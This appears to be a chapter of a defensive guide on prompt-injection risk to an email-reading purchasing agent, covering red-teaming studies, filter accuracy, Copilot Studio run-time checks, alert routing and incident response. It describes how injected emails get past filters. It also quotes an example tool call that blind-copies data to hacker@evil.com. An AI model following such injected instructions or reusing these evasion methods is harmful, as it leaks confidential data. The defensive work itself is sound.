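People did better than the software on the 29 combinations of task, model and defence that both attacked. The software succeeded against 69% of them, while at least one participant succeeded against each. The best participant among those who tried all 29 broke 75%.

Many of the successful attacks presented the attacker's request as an ordinary procedure or a necessary step in the user's own task, as the poisoned email to the purchasing agent does. A filter that receives only the text has little evidence for detecting these attacks, because real business mail contains the same sort of sentence. Other attacks imitated messages from the system itself. Where a defence depended on a hidden check, attackers who knew how the check worked could write text that stayed harmless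 while the check ran.

Nasr and colleagues did not run their search against CaMeL and similar designs that plan before reading outside text, because the attack could not have worked in most of the chosen scenarios. They add that these designs suit fewer tasks.

### LLMail-Inject: hundreds of thousands of attacks on an email assistant

*LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a challenge, organised by Microsoft researchers and outside colleagues, that is closer to the purchasing agent's situation. A simulated assistant reads a user's mail and can send email. The 839 participants wrote emails meant to make it send a message the user had not asked for. In the hardest setting, the message had to contain a profit forecast from another email in the mailbox.

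For an attack to succeed, the assistant had to retrieve the email, the defence had to miss it, and the model had to call the email tool with the right recipient and content. Participants knew which defence they faced and learned which of these steps each attack had completed, but they couldn't see the assistant's reply. They made 370,724 submissions in the main phase, from December 2024 to February 2025, and another 90,916 in a second phase against stronger defences.

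Fewer than 1% of submissions in the main phase completed every step. About 180,000 got past the defences undetected, but only 7,200 of those triggered the email tool, and about 3,000 did so correctly. Flagged submissions triggered the tool about 19% of the time, compared with 4% for undetected ones. Wording strong enough to steer the model was apparently also easier to detect.

That low success rate per submission is not very reassuring, because participants faced no penalty for failed attempts. Abdelnabi and colleagues therefore also counted how many teams eventually succeeded. In the data-theft setting with OpenAI's GPT-4o-mini, 60% of the teams that tried beat Microsoft's Prompt Shields, 32% beat an LLM judge (a language model prompted to look for injections), and 17% beat all the defences together. Across all settings, successful teams needed an average of 89 submissions to get past Prompt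 Shields and 506 to get past the judge. A few very persistent teams raised those averages, so many teams needed far fewer.

After the challenge, the researchers reran the detection defences on every submission that had triggered the email tool. They also tried them on 1,000 real business emails from the public archive of Enron, the bankrupt energy company. TaskTracker, another defence in the table, compares a model's internal activity before and after it reads outside text. The last column applies the rates measured on the Enron emails to the invented firm.

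| Defence | Detection, main phase | Detection, second phase | False positives on Enron mail | False alarms in 20,000 items |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Prompt Shields, two versions | 60–68% | 43–49% | 0% | See below |
| TaskTracker with Phi-4 | 88% | 99.8% | 5.7% | 1,140 |
| LLM judge | 99.4% | 96.5% | 5.0% | 1,000 |
| Combination, any one flags | 99.8% | Not given | 10.0% | 2,000 |

The judge catches more attacks than Prompt Shields but raises far more false alarms, as the last column shows. If 10 of the firm's items are attacks, the judge catches nearly all of them and raises about 1,000 false alarms, so its precision is roughly 1%. Prompt Shields catches about six and raises very few false alarms. The firm could let Prompt Shields block items and use the judge only before risky tool calls, where there are fewer items to check.

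A filter that raises no false alarms in 1,000 emails could still have a true false-alarm rate as high as 0.3%, or 60 a day at the firm. If the true rate is p, the chance of seeing none in n harmless items is (1 − p)ⁿ, which falls to 5% when p is about 3/n. The detection and Enron tests may also have used different thresholds, so each pair of figures is only approximate. Microsoft has had time to update Prompt Shields since the challenge ended in April 2025.

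The two studies seem to disagree about combining defences. Nasr and colleagues found that their attacks still worked against several stacked filters, but in the second phase of LLMail-Inject, nobody beat the full combination protecting GPT-4o-mini. The results probably differ partly because the LLMail-Inject defences worked in different ways from one another, and participants never received a confidence score they could use to improve their attacks. The organisers also changed several defences at once between the phases, so they cannot attribute the result to stacking alone. Combining different kinds of defence seems worthwhile if the firm can tolerate the extra false alarms, but stacking similar text classifiers probably isn't.

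The collected attacks are also hard for newer models to resist. GPT-5, set to reason at length, followed 22.8% of them, but it failed at most 0.2% of the time on the older agent benchmarks that Abdelnabi and colleagues used for comparison.

### Harmless text that looks like an attack

Outside tests of commercial injection filters are hard to find. Each of the two studies above tested a product of a company that employs some of the study's researchers, although neither product did well. *Poly-Guard* (2025) did test Amazon Bedrock Guardrails and Microsoft's Azure Content Safety, but on harmful content, which both screen for separately from injections. In two of its data sets, Bedrock's average false-positive rates were 10.9% and 15.4%, while Azure's were 0%. A 0% rate means little without the detection rate, since a filter that never flags anything scores the same.

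Research on other filters suggests that words common in injections can cause false alarms. *Safety Reconstructed* (2026) tested filters on harmless prompts containing such words. One filter, Granite, wrongly flagged 1.77% of the prompts with one such word and 10.62% of those with three. Each group had only about 113 prompts, so the difference is ten prompts, but two other filters also flagged more as the number of words rose.

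*Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) reports that combined defences flagged 5.7% of harmless retrieved texts, mostly texts containing instructions, such as technical documentation. The paper describes this rate as acceptable for most applications. At the invented firm, it would mean 1,140 false alarms a day. A purchasing department should expect a higher rate than average, because supplier mail is full of instructions ("use the new form", "send the signed copy to this address").

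### Twenty attempts against the same filter

A 90% detection rate leaves each malicious email a 10% chance of passing. If an attacker sends 20 emails and their chances are independent,

```
P(at least one passes) = 1 − 0.9²⁰ ≈ 88%
```

The 88% figure assumes that the 20 attempts are independent. If the attacker sends the same email 20 times, the filter will probably score it the same way each time, and the chance that at least one gets through stays near 10%. If the attacker learns from each failure, later emails are more likely to get through, and the total chance can exceed 88%.

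Differences between targets matter too. Suppose half of a group of agents resist every attempt and the other half give in to 20% of attempts. The average success rate is 10%, but after 20 attempts on each agent, only about 49% of the agents have failed. Published tests that average over many scenarios show the same effect. In the table, the figures for Claude Opus 4.5 come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, and those for Opus 4.6 come from VentureBeat. The rest come from Anthropic's July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5, a report on the tests the company ran on the model.

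| Model | One attempt succeeds | Attempts allowed | Expected if independent | Measured |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, operating a computer | 17.8% | 200 | Almost 100% | 78.6% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3% | 2.0% |

The formula overstates the risk in every row, but it could still understate the risk for a firm with one purchasing agent, because that agent may resemble one of the scenarios that fail quickly.

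An email that passes the filter also still has to get past the model and the rules outside it.

### How well current models resist injection

Many of these scores come from tests of the model without a separate filter. For the Opus 5 card, Anthropic used a benchmark that it built with the security company Gray Swan, the UK and US government AI institutes and other developers. The benchmark contains 1,130 attacks that people wrote for 28 scenarios in a competition, selected because they worked on several models. Within 15 attempts, an attacker succeeded against Opus 5 in 2.0% of cases and against its predecessor, Opus 4.8, in 5.5%. The rate was 16.5% for Muse Spark, the best-performing model from another company. For OpenAI's GPT-5.6, it was 20.0% for Sol, the most capable version, 30.4% for Terra and 43.9% for Luna.

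Anthropic ran the comparison itself, which is a reason for some caution. It tested its own models without extra safeguards and the others through their public services, which may include safeguards, so this difference wouldn't explain Claude's lead. However, the comparison used a fixed set of attacks that nobody adapted to each model.

The card also describes attacks with more effort behind them. The table shows Opus 5 with extended thinking, a mode in which the model reasons before acting:

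| Setting | Attempts per scenario | Successful attempts | Scenarios broken | Scenarios broken with safeguards |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Coding | 200 | 0.56% | 13 of 40 | 4 of 40 |
| Operating a computer | 200 | 0.54% | 1 of 14 | 1 of 14 |
| Web browser | 10 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

In the coding tests, "0.56% of attempts" and "a third of scenarios" describe the same result. The share of scenarios is the better guide to what a patient attacker could achieve. Anthropic points out that real attackers usually don't know the deployment and that each attempt risks detection. But it developed the coding attack on earlier models and reused it on Opus 5, and an attack developed on Opus 5 itself might do better.

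The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* took its headline from the zero in the last row. By the 3/n rule, the true failure rate could still be as high as 2.3% after no failures in 129 scenarios, even if the scenarios are typical of real use. The zero was also measured with Anthropic's auto mode, which checks incoming tool results and blocks dangerous outgoing tool calls. A firm that calls the model from its own agent shouldn't assume that it gets this protection, and without safeguards the model failed in 11 of the 129 scenarios.

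A firm can use such scores to compare models within one test. The GPT-5.6 results suggest that switching an agent from Sol to Luna to save money could more than double the success rate of these attacks. Newer or more capable models are not always more resistant. In the browser tests without safeguards, attackers succeeded in 29.7% of attempts against Claude Mythos 5 and 0.93% against Claude Sonnet 5.

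The firm can't use the scores to estimate the probability that its own purchasing agent will fail, because the agent's tools, instructions and mail differ from the test scenarios. It also can't rank vendors by comparing figures from different cards, because the number of attempts, the attackers' skill and the setting all change the result. VentureBeat notes that Anthropic's card for Opus 4.8 broke its results down by setting, while other developers' cards did not.

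### Testing the firm's own deployment

The firm therefore needs its own test, with the filter, model, tools and rules set up as they will run in production.

1. Decide what to record. For each attack, the testers note whether the filter flagged it, whether the model followed it, whether the tool call went through and whether any data left. If the policy engine stops an email that the filter missed, the filter has failed and the deployment has held.

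2. Collect harmless traffic. The sample should include emails, attachments and tool results from several weeks, in every language the suppliers use and with quoted replies left in. At least 3,000 items are necessary to show a false-positive rate below 0.1%, and then only if the filter flags none of them. People have to check the flagged items, since one could be a real attack.

3. Assemble known attacks. The LLMail-Inject collection is public and suits an email agent. Filter makers can train on it too, so a good score is only a minimum. The size of the set matters here as well: 90 catches out of 100 attacks leaves a margin of about six points either way.

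4. Authorise a red team. The owner of the agent and the head of security approve the scope in writing, and someone checks the cloud provider's rules on testing. The team works in a copy of the system with invented price agreements and sends "stolen" data only to an address the firm controls. Nasr and colleagues recommend telling human testers exactly which defences they face.

5. Give the team a budget and count its attempts. In Nasr and colleagues' tests, the automated search usually stopped improving after 100 to 200 tries, so a few dozen tries per scenario would be too few. The team should report how many attempts came before the first success and how many scenarios it broke. People should check the results, because automated scoring can count a trick as a success or miss a real one.

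6. Measure the harm to useful work. Clerks supply perhaps 200 ordinary tasks, and the agent does each one with and without the filter. A filter with few false alarms per item can still ruin many tasks, because one task may involve ten items. At a 1% false-positive rate, about 10% of such tasks would meet at least one false alarm if the errors were independent.

### Setting the threshold and testing again

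The firm can then choose a threshold by starting from the number of alarms its staff can review. Suppose the tests give these invented results:

| Flag items scoring at least | Detection rate | False-positive rate | False alarms a day | Review time at 3 minutes each |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 0.8 | 55% | 0.05% | 10 | 30 minutes |
| 0.5 | 75% | 0.4% | 80 | 4 hours |
| 0.3 | 90% | 2% | 400 | 20 hours |

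With one person available for half a day, the firm can set the threshold no lower than 0.5 for all its agents. It could use 0.3 for the purchasing agent alone if that agent reads only a small part of the 20,000 items. The firm should choose the threshold on one half of its test data and confirm it on the other; otherwise it will fit the setting to the particular emails it collected. Prompt Shields returns only true or false, so the firm cannot adjust its threshold.

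These results become outdated when the model, filter, system prompt or tools change, so the firm should repeat the known attacks and the harmless sample after each change and bring the red team back after major ones. A vendor may also update a filter without the customer noticing, so a monthly run is sensible even if the firm has changed nothing. After each run, the testers should add new attacks and recent mail so that the test set doesn't become a fixed list.

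Between those runs, the firm can send one harmless test injection through the purchasing mailbox every day. If no alarm appears, somebody may have switched off the filter, or the alarm may have gone somewhere nobody looks.

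## Connecting AI protections to the cloud security platform

Alarms should go to the cloud security platform, where the firm's security staff already work. The firm can connect an agent to that platform through run-time checks and alerts. A run-time check examines a tool call before it runs and can stop it, while an alert records a suspicious event for a person to investigate. If the purchasing agent tries to email the price agreements to an attacker at 10:14, a run-time check can prevent the theft. An alert at 10:20 comes too late to prevent it, but can help the security team find other agents that read the same email.

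### What Copilot Studio sends before each tool call

Copilot Studio can call a security service whenever an agent is about to use a tool. The service can be Microsoft Defender, another vendor's product or a program that the firm writes itself. Microsoft describes the exchange as follows:

1. The orchestrator, the part of the agent that plans its steps, chooses a tool and fills in the inputs.
2. Copilot Studio sends the proposed call to the security service.
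3. The service replies with "allow" or "block", and can add a reason.
4. If the reply is "allow", the tool runs and the user notices nothing. If it is "block", the agent stops and the user sees a notice.

The request from Copilot Studio includes the tool's name and inputs, the user's latest message, the recent conversation, the results of earlier tool calls, the agent's stated reason for choosing the tool, and the identities of the agent and user. The service can use this context to judge whether the call fits what the user asked for.

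The service also receives confidential data. If the agent has just read a price agreement, the request can include the agreement's text. When the feature launched in September 2025, Microsoft said that customers could not choose which data to share and that outside providers might store it in another region. The firm should therefore ask a provider of run-time checks the same questions about storage and retention that it asks the vendor of a mail assistant.

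Providers differ in how much of this context they use. According to CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, the security company's product analyses only the tool name and inputs, although it also logs the user's latest message and the conversation history. It can find a forbidden address or a password in an outgoing email, but it can't determine whether the user asked to email that recipient. Copilot Studio also accepts only "allow" or "block", so if a firm sets CrowdStrike's product to remove sensitive text from a call, the product reports the text but lets the call through unchanged.

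Defender uses more of the context. Microsoft gives the example of a finance agent that automatically processes every message sent to an invoice mailbox. An outsider sends what looks like an invoice, with hidden instructions to search the agent's knowledge base for unrelated sensitive information and email it to the sender. Before the search runs, Defender receives the search terms, the earlier results and the context of the email. It blocks the call, so the agent never retrieves the information.

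In another of Microsoft's examples, an employee hides instructions in a SharePoint document. The agent opens a sensitive file that the employee can't open and tries to email its contents outside the company. Defender blocks the email, but only after the agent has read the file. Microsoft doesn't publish a detection rate with these examples, so the firm should treat Defender's check as a probabilistic control.

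### An unexpected blind copy

A firm that writes its own service can make the check deterministic. Microsoft's guide for developers includes a suitable case. A user asks an agent to email a customer, and the agent asks which one. The user names John Doe, and a tool looks up his address. The agent then proposes this call:

```
tool:  Send email
to:    customer@foobar.com
bcc:   hacker@evil.com
```

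In the example, the user never asked for a blind copy, and the second address doesn't appear in the conversation or the earlier tool result. The service blocks the call and gives the noncompliant address in the blind-copy field as the reason.

Microsoft leaves the method of detection to the developer. For the purchasing agent, the service could apply the policy engine's rule that every recipient must be in the supplier directory. The rule would have to cover the "cc" and "bcc" fields as well as the "to" field, or it would not stop this theft. The service could also use a language model to check whether the call fits the user's request, but this would be slower and could give the wrong answer.

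The recipient rule still allows a reply containing prices to be sent to a supplier's hijacked mailbox. Microsoft (2026) suggests using Purview's data-loss rules, which can inspect the inputs of a tool call and block sensitive data from being sent. This helps only if a rule classifies the firm's prices as sensitive.

### When no reply arrives within a second

The service has 1,000 milliseconds to reply. After that, according to Microsoft, the agent proceeds as if the reply had been "allow". Suppose all of the invented firm's 40,000 daily tool calls go through this check and 0.5% of them time out:

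```
40,000 × 0.005 = 200 unchecked calls a day
```

Those 200 calls may not be spread evenly over the day. If the agents work steadily for eight hours, an outage of less than two and a half minutes would also leave 200 calls unchecked. Even the recipient rule would offer no protection during the outage, because nothing would enforce it.

An attacker might also be able to cause timeouts with a very long email. The request includes the results of earlier tool calls, so a service that analyses all of them could slow down. The firm should measure response times with its longest emails and contracts as well as typical ones.

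At launch, Microsoft stated that an agent assumes approval if no reply arrives in time. The developer guide still described this behaviour in June 2026, so the default does not appear to have changed. However, administrators now have a setting called "Set error behavior", which defaults to "Allow the agent to respond" and can be changed to "Block the query".

Microsoft's set-up guide is inconsistent about whether this setting covers timeouts. It says that the setting applies when the service fails to respond in time or returns an error, but a note says that the tool runs after one second without a decision. CrowdStrike says that Copilot Studio applies the configured behaviour to timeouts, which is probably right. A firm can check by selecting "Block the query" in a test environment and connecting a service that waits two seconds before it replies.

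Failing closed has a drawback too, because a timeout can stop a task partway through. If 0.5% of calls time out independently, this happens to about 5% of tasks with ten calls (1 − 0.995¹⁰). Administrators configure the check separately for each environment, so the firm could put agents that send mail or change records in an environment that fails closed and keep agents that only look up stock levels in one that fails open.

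Neither setting helps older "classic" agents, which follow fixed conversation paths, because Copilot Studio skips the check for them. The firm's inventory should therefore record which agents are classic.

### What changed in July 2026

Microsoft planned to require an Agent 365 licence from 1 July 2026 for the security features that Defender provides for Copilot Studio and Foundry agents. Tenants without one would lose those features. Microsoft's announcement lists run-time protection for Copilot Studio among these features, but also says this protection remains unchanged for tenants that use it through Defender for Cloud Apps. A firm without the licence should test whether Defender still blocks anything.

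Microsoft replaced the rules for Agent 365's own run-time protection on the same day. It warned that existing rules set to "Block" would stop blocking on 1 July and that administrators would have to recreate them on a new page. According to rodtrent, who writes about Microsoft's security products, the new default rule only records suspicious calls. If nobody recreated the firm's blocking rules, Defender may have been recording attacks since July without stopping them.

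Because the purchasing agent runs on a model in Foundry, it can't use Copilot Studio's check. Agent 365 can inspect the agent's tool calls, but only those that go through MCP servers the firm has registered or through Microsoft's Work IQ servers, which give agents access to Microsoft 365 data. rodtrent notes that calls to other tools fall outside this protection, so the firm still needs its own policy engine for them.

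### From Prompt Shields to the security team

An alert takes a different route. Microsoft connects Prompt Shields to Defender for Cloud, which watches over a company's cloud resources, and then to Defender XDR, which combines alerts from email, sign-ins, computers and cloud services. For a malicious prompt to one of the firm's models, the route looks like this:

1. Prompt Shields detects the attack, and either blocks it or only records it, depending on the firm's settings.
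2. Defender for Cloud receives the detection and can create an alert that includes evidence from the prompt. The firm must have turned on threat protection for AI services in the Azure subscription that contains the model.
3. The alert appears in Defender for Cloud and in Defender XDR.
4. Defender XDR groups it with related alerts into an incident, which an analyst opens.

If the firm collects its logs in Sentinel, Microsoft's log-analysis service, existing connectors can pass the alert on to it.

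A poisoned email is less certain to produce an alert. Microsoft's catalogue of these alerts, *Alerts for AI services*, describes the attack behind every jailbreak alert as a direct prompt injection. The February 2026 version listed no separate alert for attacks that Prompt Shields finds in documents. The table lists the alerts most relevant to the purchasing agent.

| Alert | Severity | Blocked or detected | Indirect injection? |
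| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Jailbreak attempt blocked by Prompt Shields | Medium | Blocked | No, described as direct |
| Jailbreak attempt detected by Prompt Shields | Medium | Detected but not blocked | No, described as direct |
| ASCII smuggling (instructions in invisible characters) | High | Detected | Yes |
| Malicious URL in an agent's tool response (preview) | High | Detected | Possibly, since the link came from a tool |
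| Corrupted application directed a phishing attempt at a user | High | Detected after the application shared the link | Possibly, as a result of one |
| Credential theft attempt | Medium | Detected in the model's reply | Possibly, as a result of one |
| Anomaly in sensitive data exposed by an AI resource (preview) | Medium | Detected in the model's replies | Possibly, as a result of one |
| Anomalous tool invocation | Low | Detected when the application tried to make the call | Possibly, as a result of one |

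The poisoned email has its instruction in an HTML comment and contains no invisible characters or known phishing links. The alert most likely to reveal the attack is therefore "anomalous tool invocation", which would be triggered when the agent searches for price agreements it doesn't usually need. That alert has the lowest severity in the table, so a team that opens only Medium and High alerts would miss it. The firm should raise the alert's priority for agents that can send email.

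The two jailbreak alerts have the same severity, but analysts should open the "detected" ones first and check what the model did next. In those cases Prompt Shields let the attempt through, either because of the firm's filter settings or because its confidence was low.

Severity ratings also vary between Microsoft's own publications. *The Microsoft Defender for AI Alerts* (anas_hadidi, 2025), a post on Microsoft's security blog, rates ASCII smuggling as Medium, whereas the catalogue rates it as High. Among the possible causes, the post lists an innocent user who pasted text without noticing the hidden characters. An analyst should therefore find out where the text came from before suspecting the employee named in the alert.

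Some entries in the catalogue have since changed. Microsoft planned to retire its alerts for Foundry agents in July and generate equivalent ones from Agent 365's logs, while the alerts for models would continue. In the table, this affects the alert about malicious links in tool responses and the agent versions of the jailbreak and ASCII smuggling alerts. Any automation that searches for the old alert names needs updating.

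### Microsoft 365 Copilot's records

Employees who use Microsoft 365 Copilot have a separate route to Defender, with better information about indirect injection. Microsoft records the verdicts of Copilot's own filters in a table called CloudAppEvents, which analysts can search. The field JailbreakDetected marks an attack that the user typed. XPIADetected marks one that Copilot found in a SharePoint file, and the record identifies the file. (XPIA is Microsoft's abbreviation for a cross-prompt injection attack, its name for indirect injection.)

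Defender's built-in alerts cover attempts that involve a risky user, network address or session. If an ordinary clerk opens a poisoned file from her usual computer, the attempt may appear only in the table. The firm can write a detection rule that raises an alert whenever XPIADetected is true. The firm would still need another data source for poisoned emails, since Microsoft describes this field only for SharePoint files.

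### Agents on AWS and Google Cloud

Microsoft notes that Defender for Cloud's AI alerts don't cover connected AWS accounts, so a firm with agents on Bedrock needs AWS's own services. Bedrock reports the number of guardrail interventions to CloudWatch, AWS's monitoring service, and the firm has to set an alarm there. CloudTrail records calls to AWS's interfaces, and GuardDuty searches those records for suspicious activity, such as someone removing a guardrail. Security Hub can then collect these findings with others from across AWS.

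Bedrock doesn't log the text of prompts and replies unless the firm turns on model invocation logging. Without that text, an analyst may know that a guardrail intervened but be unable to read the email that triggered it. Since the log will contain confidential mail and contracts, the firm should restrict who can open it.

On Google Cloud, Security Command Center shows findings about AI resources alongside the company's other security findings. For an investigation, the company also needs Model Armor's individual verdicts, which can go to Google's log service if an administrator enables logging in the Model Armor template.

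The three platforms therefore need different preparation. Microsoft supplies ready-made alerts for many AI attacks if the company has the right plan, licence and connectors. On AWS, the company has to create its own alarm for guardrail interventions, and on Google Cloud it has to make sure the detailed verdicts reach its analysts. A company that uses all three could send everything to one log system, but the platforms name their fields differently, so someone has to match the user, agent and time fields across them.

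### Settings that hide attacks

A protection can keep working when the security team can no longer see its alerts. According to Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime*, if the Microsoft 365 connector is disconnected, Defender still blocks suspicious tool calls in Copilot Studio, but the alerts and incidents no longer appear in the Defender portal. An attacker could try dozens of variants of an attack, each blocked, without the security team noticing.

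Other settings and conditions can have similar effects:

| Condition | Effect on visibility |
| --- | --- |
| Microsoft 365 audit logging is off | Analysts lack the activity records they need to monitor agents |
| Prompt Shields is off for a model | The jailbreak alerts that depend on its findings probably stop |
| "Security for AI Agents" is off in Defender | Defender disables all its security features for agents |
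| The tenant has no Agent 365 licence | Agent discovery and agent alerts stop |
| An attack arrives as an image or audio | Defender for Cloud doesn't scan it |
| A saved search uses the old agent table, AIAgentInfo | The search fails once Microsoft removes the table |
| A resource is new | The alert for unusual sensitive data doesn't work until Defender has learned what is normal |

Agent 365's run-time rules can also block a call without raising an alert. Microsoft replaced the old alerts with "behaviors", which are records in a searchable table called BehaviorInfo. Microsoft's overview of Defender still says Defender reports blocked actions in alerts. The firm should check whether blocked calls raise alerts in its own tenant and, if they don't, write a detection rule that searches BehaviorInfo for them.

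Alerts may also fail to appear even when the settings look correct. In *Defender for Cloud not generating alerts for Azure OpenAI jailbreak attempts*, a question on Microsoft's support forum, Bansal (2026) reported that Prompt Shields blocked his test attacks for several days but Defender for Cloud showed no alerts. A Microsoft moderator replied that Defender doesn't always create an alert for blocked or low-risk activity. That doesn't fully explain the problem, because the catalogue includes an alert for blocked jailbreaks, and the thread contains no confirmed solution. This is only one user's report, but it is a good reason to test the whole route from blocked prompt to alert.

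The daily test injection can serve this purpose if someone traces it to the analyst's screen. Some vendors provide a safe trigger for run-time checks. Palo Alto Networks' *Configure SaaS Agent Security as an External Threat Detection System* gives a harmless phrase that always produces a "block" decision when someone types it into a Copilot Studio agent. The block confirms that the connection works but doesn't measure how well the product recognises real attacks.

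### Missing audit events in Copilot Studio

Investigators also need a record of changes to the agents themselves. In August 2025, researchers at Datadog, a monitoring and security company, found that Copilot Studio wasn't recording some of these changes. Datadog's *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) describes how they created an agent, changed its settings, waited 24 hours and searched Microsoft 365's audit log. Four kinds of event that Microsoft had documented were missing:

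- changes to how users sign in to the agent
- changes to Application Insights, the service that can record the agent's conversations
- sharing the agent with other employees
- publishing a new version

An attacker with permission to edit an agent could have combined these changes by removing the sign-in requirement, turning off the recording of conversations and publishing the new version. He could then have questioned the agent from outside the company as an anonymous visitor and extracted any data it could reach. Microsoft's standard log of Copilot conversations covers only signed-in users, so it would not have recorded his questions either.

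Microsoft rated the problem "Important" and had fixed it by 5 October 2025. Datadog confirmed that all four events were being logged, but in November it found that the two that matter most in this attack, changes to sign-in and to conversation recording, were missing again. When Datadog published its findings in March 2026, both events still appeared only occasionally or not at all in its tests. Microsoft's engineers said they couldn't reproduce the problem.

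An empty search result may mean either that nobody changed an agent or that the log missed the change. Datadog suggests searching for sign-ins to Copilot Studio and general activity there, which at least shows who was using it. A firm can also save each agent's authentication settings every night and compare them with the previous night's. If an agent required a sign-in on Monday but doesn't on Tuesday, the comparison shows the change even if the audit event is missing.

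### Responding to one alert

Suppose Defender raises an "anomalous tool invocation" alert for the steel agent, one of 40 agents that share the "Supplier mail" blueprint. The firm's rule on recipients is still in a trial mode that records violations without blocking them.

#### 1. Join the logs

The analyst first has to establish whether the agent did anything harmful. She combines the alert with other records from the same morning:

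| Record | What she checks | Result in this example |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Tool calls | What the agent did before and after the alert | Read an email at 10:13, searched for price agreements, then sent an email at 10:14 |
| Sign-ins | Who used the agent, and from where | The steel clerk, at her usual computer |
| Incoming mail | Where the instruction came from | An unfamiliar domain, at 08:52, to the shared purchasing mailbox |
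| File access | What the agent opened | Three price agreements |
| Outgoing mail | Who received what | The same unfamiliar domain, with three attachments |

The ordinary sign-in suggests nobody has stolen the clerk's account. The attacker used the agent's legitimate access, so changing her password wouldn't stop the attack.

Microsoft provides a search of CloudAppEvents that lists agent activity, including tool calls. A second search, from rodtrent, matches tool calls with Defender's behaviors, but only by user over seven days. If a clerk's agent makes 80 calls a day, the search would attach all 400 calls from a working week to each behavior. Analysts should also match the agent's identity and limit the search to a few minutes around the event.

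She should save copies of the email, the conversation and the logs before anyone deletes the message. If the logs take more than about 15 minutes to assemble, or if data may still be leaving, the team should suspend the agent before continuing the investigation.

#### 2. Suspend the agent

The attacker's email is in a shared mailbox, so any of the 40 agents could read it next. The security team therefore disables the blueprint, and clerks go back to handling supplier mail themselves. If the attack were on one employee's private mailbox, disabling a single agent identity would be enough.

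The team needs the authority to do this without waiting for the head of purchasing, but she should learn about it immediately because her department has to cover the agents' work.

#### 3. Revoke tokens and secrets

The agents' existing access tokens may still work for a while, so the team also stops the agents' server and revokes the clerk's refresh tokens for the application. If the server holds passwords or keys for other systems, someone replaces them.

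The analyst also checks the three stolen files for credentials. A contract might contain a login for a supplier's ordering website, and the attacker could use that login long after the firm has fixed the agent.

#### 4. Block the attacker's address

An administrator blocks mail to and from the attacker's domain and adds the domain to the firewall's block list. The analyst searches all outgoing mail for the same domain, because another agent or an employee may have written to it. She also checks the agent's web requests, in case it sent data that way too.

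These blocks don't recover the price agreements. The firm has to assume the attacker has read them, and its lawyers should decide which suppliers to inform.

#### 5. Find every reader of the same content

The attacker probably sent the email to more than one person, so the analyst searches the mail system for the sender, the subject and a distinctive phrase from the hidden comment. In this example she finds six more copies and removes them. Attackers can vary the visible text, so a search for the subject line alone could miss some copies.

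She then searches the tool-call records for agents that opened any of the seven messages. The timber agent read one at 09:40 but took no unusual action. If an agent keeps a memory between sessions, someone deletes everything it stored after reading the email. Employees may also have opened the email with Copilot or an outside assistant, and those records are in other logs.

If an attack comes from a SharePoint file, the reference in Copilot's XPIADetected record identifies the file, and SharePoint's access log shows who else has opened it.

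#### 6. Restore the service

Before restarting the agents, the firm has to fix the weakness that the attack exploited, so it switches the recipient rule from trial mode to blocking. Testers then run the original email through a copy of the steel agent and confirm that the rule blocks the outgoing message. They add the email to the firm's collection of test attacks and check that an analyst now receives the alert at a higher priority.

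An administrator removes any permissions the agents don't need before enabling the blueprint again. The firm restarts the steel agent alone and watches its tool calls for a day, then restarts the other 39. For the first week, the software holds every outgoing email until a clerk approves it.

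## Asking users to approve individual actions

In action approval, a person approves or rejects a specific action before the agent carries it out. For example, a firm may use admin consent to let its purchasing agent send email, but a clerk must still approve the text and recipient of a particular email before the agent can send it.

In the simplest version, used in Outlook, Copilot drafts an email and the user sends it. Microsoft relies on this kind of consent where it can't sufficiently detect or limit an attack by other means, and accepts that the extra step makes the product less convenient. Approval works well for email because the user can see the recipient, text and attachments before sending, and nothing is sent if the user does nothing.

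Ordinary software, rather than the model, has to decide when to ask the user for approval. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) describes a safety researcher who told an agent to "confirm before acting". The agent began deleting messages from her real inbox anyway and continued after she told it to stop. A policy engine can hold a tool call for approval even if the model ignores such an instruction.

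### Sorting actions into three groups

Nobody can approve 40,000 tool calls a day, so the firm has to decide which actions run automatically, which need approval and which it forbids. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* gives three reasons for extra review: the action can affect another service, expose sensitive information or be difficult to undo. If an agent reads mail from strangers, the firm should also consider whether outside text has entered the session.

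The firm can put these questions to each action in order and stop at the first "yes":

1. Is the action outside the agent's job, or could one mistake cause a loss the firm can't accept? Forbid it.
2. Does it send something outside the firm, or is it hard to undo? Require approval, unless ordinary code fixes both the recipient and the content.
3. Has the session taken in outside text, and would the action change a record or show sensitive data to more people? Require approval.
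4. If every answer is no, let the action run.

Suppose the firm also wants to connect the purchasing agent to its order system. Six of the agent's actions would come out like this, assuming it has already read a supplier's email:

| Action | Can the firm undo it? | Sensitive data? | Goes outside? | Result |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Search the supplier's current contract | Nothing to undo | Yes | No | Automatic |
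| Send a standard receipt containing only the order number, to the address on file | No | No | Yes | Automatic |
| Send a supplier a reply that the model wrote | No | Possibly | Yes | Approval |
| Change a delivery date in the order system | Yes | No | No | Approval |
| Email a confidential file to an outside address | No | Yes | Yes | Forbidden |
| Change a supplier's bank details | Not after a payment | Yes | No | Forbidden |

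The contract search can stay automatic because the clerk is allowed to open the file anyway and must approve any reply the model writes afterwards. Changing the delivery date needs approval only because the session contains a stranger's email. If the clerk types the new date herself in a fresh session, the change can run immediately. The finance department still handles changes to bank details, since it can phone the supplier to confirm them.

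Three of the six actions use the same email tool, so the firm can't sort the actions by tool name alone. It should also sort them by hand. Yan had a language model classify tools from their names, descriptions and input formats, then simulated rules that blocked whole categories of action. The rules missed 14% of the tools they should have blocked.

### What the request has to show

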